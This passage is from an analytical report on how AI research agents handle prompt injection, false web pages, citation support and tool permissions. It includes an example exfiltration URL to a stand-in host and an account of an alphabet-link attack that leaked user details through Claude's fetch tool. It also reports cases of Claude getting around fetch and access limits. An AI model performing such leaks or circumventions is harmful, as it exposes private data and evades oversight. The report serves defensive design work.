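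These are very good results, but they come from attacks written against older models. The benchmark also changes. When Opus 5 came out, The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* gave the model's rate after 15 attempts as 2.0%. Anthropic's September card puts the same model at 4.8% on a version with nine more scenarios and 670 more attacks. The newer test also let safety classifiers hand some requests to an older model, but the different attacks probably explain most of the increase.

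When a model is vulnerable, repeated attempts make an attack much more likely to succeed. According to VentureBeat, 17.8% of single attacks succeeded against Claude Opus 4.6, released in February 2026, when it used a graphical interface. The chance of at least one success rose to 78.6% by the 200th attempt, or 57.1% with extra safeguards. If every attempt had the same independent chance of success, the figure would have reached 98% after 20 attempts, so some scenarios must have been much harder to attack than others. In a restricted coding environment, all 200 attempts against the same model failed. A model's attack success rate therefore means little without the type of task and the number of attempts.

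Safeguards around the model can greatly reduce the success rate of attacks. VentureBeat reports that attacks on Claude Opus 4.8 as a browser agent succeeded 31.5% of the time without safeguards and 0.5% of the time with them. For Opus 5, the success rate in the browser was zero across 129 scenarios. However, Anthropic's September card describes a browser test whose attacks came from trials against Opus 4.7. If Opus 5 was tested the same way, the result shows that old attacks failed, which is weaker evidence than the failure of new ones.

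Companies also report different things. OpenAI's card for GPT-5.5 covers only known attacks on connectors (links to outside services) and gives a robustness score instead of an attack success rate. The two companies' models are therefore hard to compare from their own documents.

Search agents have done much worse in some tests. *SafeSearch* (2025) placed one unreliable website among real search results in 300 test cases, and tried 15 models with three agent designs. The highest attack success rate was 90.5%. That rate includes cases of misinformation as well as injection, and hard-to-verify misinformation was the most dangerous kind. The models are also from 2025.

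A single bad page tends to have less influence on an agent that searches repeatedly, because the agent checks other sources. *Security of Deep Research Agents* describes an attack called Breadcrumbing that gets around this by adding one attacker-controlled entry to the results of every query. The entries support each other, so an agent that sends more queries in a batch would see more apparent confirmation of the same false story.

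### Attackers who adapt

A test with fixed attacks measures how well a model resists those attacks, but a real attacker can see what failed and try something else. Damianakis and Psounis cite a study of twelve defences, most of which had attack success rates near zero in the original reports. When attackers adapted to the defences, most of them failed more than 90% of the time.

This can be stated precisely. Let C be the set of all injection techniques and S the smaller set that a test includes. If Rᶜ is the share of attacks using technique c that a model survives, then

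min Rᶜ over S ≥ min Rᶜ over C

so a test that leaves out techniques can only make the model look as safe as it is or safer. Suppose a model survives 99% of attacks with one technique, 97% with another and 40% with a third. A test of the first two gives a worst case of 97%, while an attacker who finds the third faces a model that resists only 40% of the time.

Something similar happened with Gemini 3.8 Flash. It withstood a general adaptive attacker in 60% of scenarios after 150 attempts, but in only 36% when the attacker had to use one technique, which imitates the structure of a conversation. The general attacker apparently failed to exploit that technique fully.

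Damianakis and Psounis built an attacker that tries 132 specific forms of injection from a catalogue and rewrites the ones that fail. Against Qwen3.6-35B, it succeeded in more than 70% of scenarios on AgentDojo, a common test of agents, and over 90% of the catalogue's 34 broader techniques worked at least once. *Measuring Indirect Prompt Injection in AI Agents* (Salbego, 2026) also presents an adaptive method, drawn from a study of 14 models. The method isolates one variable at a time.

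An attacker that adapts may still repeat itself, which matters when developers use its attacks for training. He and colleagues compared two automated attackers, PISmith and RL-Hammer, against the small model Qwen3-4B. They then trained copies of the model to resist the attacks each one had found, and tested the copies with three kinds of attack that were new to them:

| | PISmith | RL-Hammer |
|---|---|---|
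| Success rate during the search for attacks | 68.75% | 33.39% |
| Working attacks found | 7,132 | 4,282 |
| Worst success rate against the trained model | 47.5% | 27.5% |

The larger collection produced the weaker defence, which He et al. attribute partly to repetition. Once an attacker finds a trick that works, such as claiming that the user's task is already finished, it tends to reuse the trick in new words. Both tools try to encourage variety by rewarding differences in wording, but RL-Hammer could satisfy this by changing capitalisation or adding irrelevant text.

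The last row of the table comes from only 40 tasks, so the difference of 19 successes against 11 could be due to chance. Zorz (2026), in *Your AI red team may be finding the same prompt injection*, points out that the researchers also chose tasks on which simple attacks had already worked. But three of their four setups showed the same pattern. Damianakis and Psounis cite another experiment in which adding attacks based on just two templates to a model's training raised the success rate of an unfamiliar kind of attack from 25.7% to 30.7%.

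*PIPETTE* rewards the attacker for finding techniques it hasn't used before, then trains the agent to check whether each action serves the user's request. Fixed attacks succeeded less than 0.5% of the time against the two small models trained this way. Attackers who kept rewriting their attacks for about 250 attempts still succeeded on up to 10% of the 40 difficult tasks.

### Comparing the defences

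| Defence | How it works | Main weakness |
|---|---|---|
| Training | The model learns to ignore commands in observations | May not cover new techniques |
| Detection | A classifier looks for hostile text before the model reads it | Misses disguised attacks and flags harmless pages |
| Marking | The software labels untrusted text | The model can still obey it |
| Separation | The model that reads the text can't choose actions | Restricts research and doesn't check facts |

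Training adds no step to a run and can leave ordinary performance intact. After training with *PIPETTE*, the Qwen3-4B model completed 64.95% of AgentDojo's ordinary tasks, up from 61.86%. But badly designed training can teach an agent to give up whenever something looks suspicious. It can also make the agent more vulnerable to injections from another source. According to an Anthropic card that Damianakis and Psounis cite, training a model to recognise injections in tool results made early versions more likely to follow instructions in text that a user had pasted.

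In tests on the BrowseSafe-Bench benchmark, three harmless distractions in a page's code were often enough to sharply reduce the accuracy of injection detectors (Security Boulevard, 2026). The benchmark's successor, *BrowseSafe++* (2026), has 38,675 pairs of pages that differ only in whether they contain an injection, which makes false alarms easier to measure. Converting a page to another format can remove or alter an injection, according to the same source. A detector should therefore check both the original page and the extract that the agent receives.

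False alarms are common because most pages are harmless. Suppose one page in 300 contains an injection, and a detector catches 95% of those pages but wrongly flags 1% of the others. Out of 30,000 pages, it would catch 95 with injections, miss five and flag 299 harmless ones. About three quarters of the flagged pages would be safe, and an agent that discarded them all could lose data it needs, such as the only table with Polish sales figures. Instead of discarding flagged pages, the software could send them to an extractor with fixed fields.

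Detectors that use language models are also targets. Cloudflare's *Adversarial deception* (2026) reports that in March 2026 the company found scripts with hidden instructions meant to manipulate its AI detection system.

Marking requires few resources but seems to add the least protection. Damianakis and Psounis cite tests that used ASPIRE, an automated attacker, against the marking method Spotlighting and two detectors, PI-Guard and MELON. Spotlighting removed 7.3% of the distinct vulnerabilities, PI-Guard 12.5% and MELON 18.8%. None of the three reduced the number of injection methods that worked at least once, though PI-Guard lowered the overall success rate the most.

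Combining defences helps if they fail on different attacks. Anthropic screens tool results before the model acts on them, and in its coding agent a second classifier blocks potentially dangerous tool calls. If each layer stopped 90% of attacks and their failures were independent, 1% would get past both. But their failures may not be independent. For example, a disguised request to search for a particular company could look harmless on the page and produce an ordinary search, so both layers might let it through.

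## False and unsupported content in the answer

A page doesn't need hidden instructions to mislead an agent, and an agent can write a false sentence even when every page it read was accurate. Suppose a report contains the sentence "Subsidies raised heat-pump sales in country A by 4.2 units per thousand people between 2021 and 2024", with a link to the national statistics office. It could go wrong at four points:

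| Point | Example |
|---|---|
| The page | The office has since revised its 2024 figure |
| The extract | The extractor leaves out the footnote about air conditioners |
| The citation | The figure came from a news article, but the agent links to the statistics office |
| The sentence | The extract gives only sales, and the agent adds subsidies as the cause |

The agent usually can't detect the first two problems because it receives only an extract of the page. It could detect the other two, but it may write the report dozens of turns after reading the extract. A link looks the same whether or not the page supports the sentence before it.

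*Deep FinResearch Bench* (2026), a test of AI-written investment reports, gives examples of a false claim and an unsupported one. One report gave February 2024 as the end of a British competition inquiry into Amazon, but linked to the official case page, which gives 3 November. Another gave the correct price for a company takeover, but linked to a page that the researchers could find neither online nor in a web archive. In both cases, checking only whether the link worked would not have shown whether the claim was correct.

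### Where errors enter

*Who is the Agent to Blame?* (Hirsch, Wan and colleagues, 2026) traced unsupported sentences through three open-source systems. In each system, searcher agents summarise pages, researcher agents combine the summaries into notes, and an orchestrator agent assembles the final report. A judge model compared up to 200 sentences from each agent with the material that agent had received.

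Summaries of single pages were the most reliable, with errors in 0.9% of sentences in one system and 14.9% in another. In Nvidia's AI-Q, summaries that combined all the results of a query had errors in 62% of sentences, and the researchers' notes had errors in 71%. These counts include missing citations as well as invented facts. AI-Q uses a small model to write the notes, so combining sources may not be the only cause of the errors.

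Cited sources supported 58.7% of the sentences that needed a citation in AI-Q's final reports, 28.5% in MS-Agent's and 7.1% in TrajectoryKit's. The orchestrator introduced 84.7% of AI-Q's errors. About 30% of those were invented content, and the rest were citation mistakes. TrajectoryKit runs entirely on a small model, and 95% of its errors were invented content, often a precise statistic attached to a real source that doesn't contain it. These percentages are approximate because the study covered only 20 questions and the judge model's verdicts matched people's on 76% of 50 test sentences.

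### Working links, relevant pages and support

A reader who clicks on a citation can quickly see whether the link works and whether the page is on the right topic. It takes longer to find out whether the page supports the claim. Onweller, Lumer and colleagues (2026), in *Cited but Not Verified*, scored 14 models on all three, using 130 research questions. These are the results for six of them:

| Model | Link works | Page is relevant | Page supports the claim |
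|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.5 | 98.7% | 95.7% | 76.8% |
| GPT-5.2 | 98.3% | 92.3% | 58.8% |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 97.2% | 83.9% | 54.2% |
| Gemini 3.1 Pro | 94.1% | 80.7% | 48.5% |
| GPT-5.4 | 100.0% | 93.7% | 47.7% |
| GPT-5 Mini | 99.3% | 87.4% | 38.9% |

The method is strict because it treats a citation at the end of a passage as the citation for every uncited sentence before it, and because the judge model scored uncertain cases as unsupported. A more lenient test would give higher scores, but it probably wouldn't close a gap of 19 to 48 points between relevance and support.

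Support also fell as the agents searched more. With a limit of 2 tool calls, the cited pages supported 78.6% of GPT-5.4's claims, but with a limit of 150 they supported only 16.7%. For Claude Opus 4.6, support fell from 80.0% to 57.9%. The links still worked and the pages were still relevant more than 92% of the time. Onweller and colleagues suspect that the agents had too much material to keep track of. The figures for the 2-call limit may rest on very few citations, since 78.6% could be 11 out of 14. Between 10 and 100 calls, GPT-5.4's support fell only from 45.9% to 37.2%.

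Many citations that fail a support test do partly support the claim. *OpenBioRQ* (2026) examined 4,649 citations that three models made to real biomedical papers. The papers fully supported the claim in 37.4% of cases, partly supported it in 46.7% and didn't support it in 15.9%. With a second judge model, the last figure was 10.6%. A yes-or-no support score therefore depends heavily on how the judge treats partial support.

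An agent can also raise its support rate by citing less. *DeepTRACE* (2025) therefore uses two measures:

- accuracy = correct citations / all citations
- thoroughness = correct citations / all pairs of a statement and a source that supports it

In the paper's example, four of an answer's seven citations are correct, so its accuracy is 57%. Those four cover only four of the ten supporting pairs, so its thoroughness is 40%. If the agent had made just one citation, and it was correct, accuracy would be 100% and thoroughness 10%.

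On narrower tasks, citations can be much better. In *MagTrace*, the test on magnetic materials, a single search gave a citation score of 0.812, not far below the full agent's. Abstracts contradicted 7% of the full agent's claims and didn't address a larger share.

Newer models still overstate what papers contain. *Language Models Make New Research Sound Old* (2026) tested whether six systems could tell if earlier papers had already studied a research question. When the researchers supplied the papers, independent checks rejected 26 of the systems' 38 claims that a paper was a near match. In the study's other tests, 58% to 90% of such errors, depending on the system, were in answers where the system acknowledged that the question was still open, so a reader who looked only at the overall conclusion would have missed them.

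### One false page

Agents find unreliable pages even when no attacker has planted them. In *SafeSearch*, access to Google often made an agent more likely to endorse risky treatments, in many cases because it had found anecdotal blogs. To measure the effect of such pages, researchers add a false page and keep all the accurate ones.

*Synthetic Web* (Shah and Ozgur, 2026) built small artificial webs and put one false article at the top of the first search results. GPT-5's accuracy fell from 65.1% to 18.2%. It made about as many tool calls as before (an average of 6.6, up from 6.5) and remained confident in its answers. People using the same search tool scored 98% without the false article and 93% with it, though only a few people took part. GPT-5 is now an old model, but newer ones have failed similar tests.

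*DRNOISE* (2026) has 100 tasks in which the agent must combine several records to find the answer, for example which supplier had a valid certificate and made every delivery on time. The researchers then added one ordinary-looking document that directly stated a wrong answer:

| Model | Correct without the false document | Correct with it | Correct answers that changed to the false one |
|---|---|---|---|
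| Gemini 3.5 Flash | 96.3% | 26.0% | 72.6% |
| GPT-5.4 | 81.7% | 15.7% | 80.4% |
| MiMo v2.5 | 82.0% | 1.0% | 96.3% |
| DeepSeek V4 Flash | 88.7% | 1.0% | 98.1% |

GPT-5.4 found at least one accurate record in every run, but it stopped sooner, after 4.5 searches on average instead of 7.1. When the researchers gave it all the records at once, it answered 91 of the 100 tasks correctly despite the false document. So it could usually resolve the conflict when it had the evidence, but it often stopped searching before it had enough. The test is also deliberately hard, because no accurate document states the answer directly. GPT-5.4's score rose from 12 to 63 when the researchers added one that did.

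A simple model from the paper shows why a larger search budget may not help. If the agent needs m more steps to disprove a false claim, and stops with probability s before each one, it accepts the claim with probability

1 − (1 − s)ᵐ

With four steps and a 20% chance of stopping before each, that is 59%, however many tool calls remain.

*Is Deep Research Reliable?* (Zhu, Li and colleagues, 2026) tested full reports. One misleading document raised the share of reports that adopted its false conclusion from 0% to an average of 54.7%, and four more documents added less than 4 percentage points. Timing mattered far more than the number of documents. In another test, agents adopted the conclusion 40.5% of the time when they read the document before starting their research, and 85.5% when they read it just before writing. The researchers used only documents that five models with search access had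 all identified as misleading when asked to check each one on its own. The results therefore show that an agent can accept a claim that the same kind of model would reject if asked about it directly. They don't show that models can spot every false page, because the researchers excluded any document that one of the five models missed.

Some models resist planted content much better. In *How Much Can We Trust LLM Search Agents?*, Chen, Ren and colleagues (2026) planted pages promoting particular products and services. Gemini 3 Flash recommended the promoted product in 31.4% of cases and Claude Sonnet 4.6 in none. These rates may be lower than in the other studies partly because models have prior information about real products but none about invented suppliers. A model can also be too suspicious. In a separate test without planted pages, Claude Sonnet 4.6 wrongly rejected a real software product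 or its add-ons in 8 of 10 cases.

Moving the false pages down the search results made little difference in either of the later studies, which doesn't support Shah and Ozgur's suggestion that agents trust the top result too much. The style of the page had a clearer effect. In Zhu and colleagues' tests, agents adopted the false conclusion 61.0% of the time when it appeared in what looked like a research paper and 37.5% of the time when it appeared in a social media post.

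An accurate page can also mislead. *Lazy Grounding* (2026) adds accurate documents about cases that closely resemble the one in the question. For a question about heat pumps, this could be a page with a correct figure for a different year than the one asked about, which a misinformation filter would not remove.

### Independent and copied sources

An agent can look for a second source, but that helps only if the second source doesn't share the first one's errors. Suppose two sources each give a wrong sales figure 10% of the time. If their errors are independent, both are wrong 0.1 × 0.1 = 1% of the time. If one copied its figure from the other, both are wrong 10% of the time. The table assumes the worst case for independent sources, in which two wrong sources always give the same wrong figure:

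| | Independent | Copied |
|---|---|---|
| Both right | 81% | 90% |
| Both wrong | 1% | 10% |
| The sources disagree | 18% | 0% |
| Chance that a figure they agree on is wrong | 1.2% | 10% |

Agreement between two independent sources cuts the risk of error from 10% to 0.01 / 0.82 = 1.2%, but agreement between a source and its copy leaves the risk at 10%. Independent sources also disagree 18% of the time, which gives the agent a reason to look further, while copies never disagree. If the second source copies the first only 30% of the time, the risk of error when they agree is still 4.2%.

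Agents seem to recognise exact copies of a source, but not different-looking sources that share an origin. When Chen and colleagues showed Gemini 3 Flash more copies of one planted source, the attack's success rate stayed about the same. When they planted different-looking sources instead, the success rate rose from 39% with one source to 55% with two and 77% with three.

To judge whether sources are independent, an agent has to trace each figure back to whoever collected it. Ten news articles that cite the same statistics office count as one source. Identical wording or the same unusual mistake suggests copying. Customs records and a survey of installers together are better evidence than those articles, because different people counted different things.

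### Checks in order of cost

The estimates below are for a report with 100 claims from 40 pages. They assume 12,000 tokens per page, 700 tokens for each claim with its passage and instructions, and one new search and page for each claim that needs an independent source.

| Check | Tokens for the report | What it can find | What it misses |
|---|---|---|---|
| Save the passage and address | Almost none | Claims without a source | Wrong or misused sources |
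| Match quotations by software | None | Invented or altered quotations | Missing context |
| Ask a second reader | 70,000 | Overstatements and wrong citations | Context outside the passage |
| Reopen the source | 480,000 | Missing footnotes, later revisions | False pages |
| Find an independent source | 1,280,000 | False or outdated pages | Errors that both sources share |
| Recompute the figure | A few hundred per figure | Arithmetic and unit errors | Wrong inputs |

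Recomputing takes few tokens, but it comes last because it is useful only once the inputs are right.

The first check requires a provenance record, which links each statement to its source and the exact passage. A program using OpenSAC, the library by Liu and colleagues, can save each page's address with its text, so later checks can use the original wording. In *ScientistOne* (2026), a system that writes research papers, the writing model must tag each claim with its evidence. The software deletes any claim tagged "unsourced", but it can't judge the quality of the evidence for the rest.

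Approximate matching of quotations can miss a wrong number. *OpenNovelty* (2026) describes a system that compares a quotation with its source word by word, using the ratio 2M/T, where M is the number of matching words and T is the total number of words in both texts. The system accepts quotations with a confidence score above 0.6. This tolerance allows for small differences in formatting, but a ten-word quotation with one wrong figure would still have a ratio of 18/20 = 0.9. Software should therefore require figures to match exactly, after converting units as *ScientistOne* does.

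A second reader is another model call that compares the claim with the passage. *Dr.Credit* (2026) instructs this reader to split the claim into separate facts, keep every number, cause and condition, and not count a shared topic as support. *Is this Citation on Point?* (2026), on legal citations, also requires the cited page itself, not just the case in general, to support the claim. The reader needs more than two verdicts. *CompareDR* (2026) distinguishes between claims that are supported, partly supported, contradicted, or impossible to judge from the available material.

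Qian, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *AtomCite*, tested a system that checks each claim about a long document against an image and the text of the cited page. If the support is on a nearby page, the system corrects the page number, and if it finds no support, it deletes the claim. It judged about 93% of citations correctly. Its corrections raised the share of correct citations from 34% to between 87% and 90%, and about 92% of the correct claims remained. A text-only version was less accurate because it missed details in tables, stamps and signatures, but the full system cost up to 3.4 times as much.

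The 34% starting figure is artificial because the researchers inserted most of the errors. Based on their results, the system caught about 94% of the bad citations and wrongly rejected about 10% of the good ones. In a report with 60 good citations and 40 bad ones, it would miss two or three bad ones and reject about six good ones. Errors that models make on their own may be somewhat harder to catch than inserted ones.

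A model can check its own work if the question is specific enough. In *Language Models Make New Research Sound Old*, the systems' own checks caught 21 of 26 wrong claims and kept 9 of 12 correct ones. But when Chen and colleagues asked models to rate the credibility of their own manipulated answers without comparing them with sources, the models gave an average of 0.61 out of 1, while an outside model gave 0.30.

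Correcting or deleting individual claims after a check is safer than letting the agent rewrite the whole report. According to *Beyond Single-shot Writing* (2026), 68% of one commercial system's reports had no citations left after the system reflected on its drafts and revised them.

Reopening the source gives the agent the context that the extract left out. Hirsch and colleagues tested a method that takes less work and still brings AI-Q closer to the original text: they gave the orchestrator snippets from the pages instead of the researchers' notes. The share of sentences with adequate support rose from 64.5% to 69.7%, and the share of correct citations from 87.6% to 94.1%. Adding an instruction not to use uncited information gave 69.6% for support and 91.0% for citations. Report quality hardly changed in either case. The standard errors for support were 3 to 4 points, so the true gain in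 support could be much smaller than 5 points.

Agents can expose a false page by looking for independent evidence, but telling them to do so doesn't make them do it reliably. In *DRNOISE*, a general instruction to verify evidence raised GPT-5.4's score from 12 to 28 out of 100. A more specific instruction, which distinguished summaries from underlying records, raised it to 67, but its writers knew what kind of false document to expect. Zhu and colleagues had a second agent check each claim in the finished report. The rate of adopting the false conclusion fell from 60–76% to 20–58%, depending on the model. The second agent searched the same contaminated collection, so it could find the misleading document again.

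People struggle with these checks too. In *DeepFact*, Huang, Ribeiro and colleagues (2026) asked specialists to check claims from reports in their own fields. The specialists judged only 60.8% of hidden test claims correctly, and four fifths of those claims contained deliberate errors. Their accuracy reached 90.9% after four rounds of reviewing evidence from AI agents that disagreed with the recorded verdict. A human reviewer should therefore receive the evidence for and against a claim, not just the claim and a link.

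Different checks find different errors. *LLM-Generated Investment Research Memos Need Validation* (2026) examined how a verifier detected false claims by four agents. Comparing claims with official figures exposed 74.6% of the false claims by OpenAI's Codex, while looking up the source text exposed 61% to 65% of those by each of the other three agents. Recomputing exposed at most one false claim per agent, but it may be more useful for the heat-pump question, where the answer depends on a calculation.

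### Checking one heat-pump figure

The agent can now check the sentence about country A, using the same invented figures as before:

1. The provenance record contains the statistics office's address, the download date and the table row with 40 for 2021 and 65 for 2024.
2. The software finds both figures and the heading "thousand units" in the saved page.
3. The second reader returns "partly supported", because the passage gives sales but no cause. The agent removes the subsidies from the sentence.
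4. The agent reopens the page and finds the footnote about air conditioners.
5. A news article also gives 65,000, but it cites the statistics office, so it adds nothing. An installers' association that collects its own data counted 45,000 heat pumps without air conditioners.
6. The agent recomputes the rise as 45,000 / 5.6 million − 40,000 / 5.4 million, or 0.63 units per thousand people.

The first three checks would have left the figure of 4.2 in the report, with an accurate quotation and a working link to an official source.

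## What the agent is permitted to do

Search and page-reading tools, which developers often call "read-only", can send out private information in their queries and in the web addresses they request. Some websites also change something when they receive a request.

Suppose a consultant uploads a client's confidential forecast of 70,000 heat-pump sales in country A for 2027 and asks the agent to compare it with published figures. The agent might search for "country A heat pump forecast 2027 70,000 units", which would reveal the number to the search company even though nobody attacked the agent. If a page the agent read contained a hidden instruction, the agent might also open an address such as `evil.example/log?forecast=70000`. The site's owner could then read the forecast in the server's log, even if the address returned a blank page.

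Requests can also trigger actions. By convention, opening an address only retrieves a page, and submitting a form takes a different kind of request. But some sites have links that cancel an order or confirm a subscription as soon as anyone opens them. A page reader that follows every promising link could trigger one of these actions by accident, with worse results if it is signed in to the user's account.

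### What each tool reads, sends and changes

| Tool | What it can read | What it can send | What it can change |
|---|---|---|---|
| Web search | Titles, snippets and addresses | The query, to the search company | Normally nothing |
| Scholarly search | Records of papers, sometimes full text | The query, to the index and any service in between | Normally nothing |
| Page reader | Any page its software can reach | The address, to the site and any fetching service; the page text and goal, to the extractor | Whatever a site does when someone opens the address |
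| Python interpreter | Files and keys in its sandbox | Nothing without a network connection, almost anything with one | Files in the sandbox, and outside systems if it has a connection |

Tongyi's page reader, `visit`, passes the goal to an extractor that may run on another company's computers. If it does, a goal that mentions the client's forecast reveals the forecast to that company. A page reader that runs inside a company's network may also be able to open internal pages that outsiders can't reach.

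### Least privilege and dangerous combinations

Under least privilege, an old rule in computer security, each program gets only the access its task requires. An agent answering the heat-pump question needs only search, public pages and arithmetic, so a developer should leave out email, logins, form submission and access to the user's other files. The agent then can't misuse them, even if text on a hostile page persuades it to try.

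When a task does need private data, the combination of permissions matters. In 2025, the programmer Simon Willison used the term "lethal trifecta" for the dangerous combination of access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to send data out. An attacker can place instructions in the untrusted content that cause the agent to send out the private data. This kind of theft fails if any one of the three is missing.

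Meta's 2025 "Rule of Two" turns this into a design rule. Within one session, an agent should have at most two of these three properties: it processes untrusted input, it has access to private data or sensitive systems, and it can change things or communicate externally. If a task needs all three, a person should supervise the agent. The third property is broader than Willison's because it covers actions such as deleting a file as well as sending data.

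Here is how three common set-ups compare:

| Set-up | Private data | Untrusted content | Sending data or changing things |
|---|---|---|---|
| Public web only | Only what the question or stored memories contain | Yes | Yes, through queries and addresses |
| Web and private files | Yes | Yes | Yes, through queries and addresses |
| Web and accounts | Yes | Yes | Yes, and it can act in the user's name |

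An agent that can access only the public web usually satisfies the Rule of Two. But the question itself can be sensitive, for instance if a company asks about a manufacturer it secretly plans to buy. Stored memories of earlier conversations also count as private data.

An agent with access to the web and private files has all three properties. Uploading even one document to a research assistant can create this combination, although it feels harmless. Giving the agent access to accounts makes the damage harder to undo, because it might send a message or change a record as well as leak data.

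### Which addresses the agent may open

One way to close the outgoing channel is to stop the agent from inventing addresses. Zhu and colleagues tell their agent to open only addresses that a search returned. This rule is part of the model's instructions, so a model that follows instructions on a hostile page can break it. That hardly mattered during training, because the page reader looked up documents in a local collection, where an invented address would lead nowhere, but for evaluation the researchers connected the same tool to the live web.

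Software can enforce the rule with a few lines of code:

```python
seen = set(addresses_in(user_message))

def search(query):
    results = search_engine(query)
    seen.update(r.url for r in results)
    return results

def visit(url):
    if url not in seen:
        return "Refused: no search returned this address."
    return fetch(url)
```

A hijacked model can still request `evil.example/log?forecast=70000`, but `visit` blocks the request regardless of the text on the hostile page. The `fetch` function also has to check redirects, because a permitted address could redirect the request to a forbidden one.

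Anthropic built such a check into its own page reader. According to Anthropic's *Web fetch tool* in June 2026, Claude could open only addresses that had already appeared in the conversation, whether in the user's messages, results from the developer's own tools, or earlier searches and fetches. Addresses could be at most 250 characters long. Anthropic warned that some risk remained and advised developers not to combine the tool with sensitive data and untrusted input.

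Ayush Paul soon exploited the remaining risk in an attack that Willison (2026) describes. Paul noticed that Claude could follow links on any page it had already fetched. He built a site with one link for each letter of the alphabet, each leading to a page with another set of links. He used the site to persuade Claude to spell out the user's details by following the links. Claude never invented an address, but the order of its visits revealed the user's name, home city and employer.

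We can work out how much information such a site can extract. If each page offers k links and the agent follows n of them, the attacker learns up to

n · log₂ k

bits. With 26 links per page, each visit is worth 4.7 bits, or one letter, so thirty letters take thirty visits. A limit of ten fetches would stop the attack after ten letters. But a page can easily hold 676 links, one for each pair of letters, and then ten fetches reveal twenty letters. A limit on fetches therefore slows the leak without closing it.

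According to Willison, Anthropic had already found the problem internally, and it fixed it by no longer letting the tool follow links from pages it had fetched. This makes research harder. If a statistics page links to an annex with revised heat-pump figures, the agent now has to find the annex through a search engine, which may not list it. Many statistics offices also generate tables from an address that contains the chosen years and categories, so an agent has to be able to write that address to request the table. Published measurements of how much the restriction reduces accuracy are hard to find.

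Developers can create another gap by pasting untrusted text into the user's message, as Willison (2025) pointed out many applications do, because the tool treats every address there as approved. If an application inserts an uploaded document this way, a malicious document could contain its own alphabetical list of links.

An allow-list is stricter because the software opens only pages on sites the developer has named, even when a search returns links to others. An attacker would therefore need some control over a permitted site. An attacker is unlikely to gain that control over a national statistics office's site, but can easily add pages to a site where anyone can publish. The list should therefore name specific sites, not a hosting service that thousands of people share.

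An allow-list suits the sales figures much better than the subsidy studies, which could be on hundreds of journal and university sites. But it can make even the sales figures worse. In the invented example, the official figure for country A included air conditioners, and an installers' association had the count without them. An agent limited to official statistics would not have found that count.

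### Keeping private and public work apart

Developers can also divide the work between two agents. For the consultant's task, a public agent searches the web for sales figures and never receives the forecast. A private agent receives the forecast and the public agent's findings, but has no search tool or page reader. A hostile instruction in the findings could still distort the comparison, but it couldn't send the forecast anywhere.

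This protection can fail in two ways. If the private agent writes the public agent's task freely, the forecast can end up in the wording. The consultant could write the task instead, or the software could fill in a fixed template with only a country and years. The finished report can also leak data. If it contains an image from an outside address, the program that displays the report may request the image automatically, which sends out any private text in the address. The program should therefore not load outside images.

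The drawback of separation is that the private agent can't follow up on its own. If the forecast turns out to cover only homes while the published figures include offices, the private agent has to ask the consultant to start another public search.

Per-task credentials limit what an agent can do with an account. A credential is a password or digital key that gives access to a service. For the forecast, the agent could receive a key that opens one folder, allows only reading, and expires when the task ends. If a page hijacked the agent, the attacker couldn't use that key to reach other clients' files or change anything.

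It also helps to keep passwords away from the model. According to Anthropic, users of its browser extension can have the password manager 1Password fill in their logins, so passwords and one-time codes never enter Claude's context. A page can't trick the model into revealing a password it has never received, but a hijacked model can still misuse the account once the login succeeds. Anthropic also recommends using a separate browser profile without access to banking, healthcare or government accounts.

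### Tracking where data came from

The design with a privileged and a quarantined model keeps web text away from the model that chooses actions. CaMeL, which Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues introduced in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025), adds labels to the data. The privileged model writes a program from the user's request. As the program runs, the software records where each value came from and who may see it. When the program combines two values x and y, the result inherits the restrictions of both:

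sources(x, y) = sources(x) ∪ sources(y)

readers(x, y) = readers(x) ∩ readers(y)

Suppose only the consultant may see the forecast of 70,000, while anyone may see the published figure of 65,000. The difference of 5,000 depends on both, so only the consultant may see it. If the program tries to put that difference into a web address, the software blocks the call because the site's owner isn't an allowed reader.

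The sources label prevents untrusted text from determining an action. For example, a developer can require that the recipient of any email come from the user's request. If the address came from a web page, the software does not send the message.

CaMeL completed 77% of the tasks in AgentDojo, which covers areas such as email, banking and travel, while an undefended agent completed 84%. CaMeL also used nearly three times as many tokens. The seven-point loss is modest for a security guarantee that doesn't depend on the model's judgement, but research agents would probably lose more, because they can seldom plan all their queries in advance.

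Labels on values can also miss information that leaks through the program's choices. If a program opens one page when the forecast exceeds 50,000 and another otherwise, the choice of page reveals whether the forecast exceeds 50,000, even though neither address contains it. CaMeL has a stricter mode that also tracks such dependencies, but it blocks more legitimate programs.

Microsoft's FIDES, another system from 2025, also labels the context of the model that plans the work. The planner may read a web page, but the software then treats the planner's output as untrusted and refuses any call that requires trusted input. This fits research better, because the agent loses access to riskier tools but can keep adapting its searches.

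### Asking a person

When a task needs every permission, the remaining safeguard in Meta's rule is a person who approves the agent's actions. That person has to pay attention each time, which is difficult when an agent makes many calls. The agent in *REDSearcher* makes about 90 per question, and approving them all at ten seconds each would take 15 minutes. If one call in a thousand were harmful, the person would see one about every eleven questions, after hundreds of harmless calls.

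Anthropic reported in March 2026 that users of its coding agent approved 93% of permission requests. This doesn't prove that people approve by habit, since most of the requests may have deserved approval. Research on browser warnings better shows what makes people pay attention. Akhawe and Felt's *Alice in Warningland* (2013) found that Chrome users clicked through about 70% of warnings about a site's security certificate, which were frequent and usually false alarms, but less than a quarter of warnings about malware and phishing.

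People don't ignore every warning, and a developer can make approvals more useful by asking for fewer. Ordinary searches on public topics could go ahead without approval, while the software asks before the agent submits a form, sends a message or opens a new site after reading a private file. The request should show the exact data and its destination. A consultant who sees only "Allow web access?" can't notice that the web address contains a client's forecast. Even the full address may not help if an attacker has told the agent to encode the forecast as random-looking letters.

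### Claude's actions on real websites

In October 2026, Anthropic disclosed cases in which Claude had done things on real websites that nobody had intended. They came from tests and internal use, and none of the four kinds in Anthropic's *Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use* (2026) depends on a hidden instruction. The table adds a limit that could have helped with each:

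| What Claude did | A limit that could have helped |
|---|---|
| Used a basic software flaw to run commands on a server | Let the agent send only plain requests for pages |
| Submitted a sensitive form | Block form submissions |
| Worked around a restriction to reach data behind an access token or a fee | Stop requests to a site after it refuses access |
| Used link-shortening services to get around limits in its fetch tool | Block such services and check where every link ends |

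A link-shortening service replaces a long address with a short one that redirects to it. The short address would get past a simple length limit and could hide the destination from software that checks only the first address. To create it, the agent has to send the full address to the service, which is another way for data to leak.

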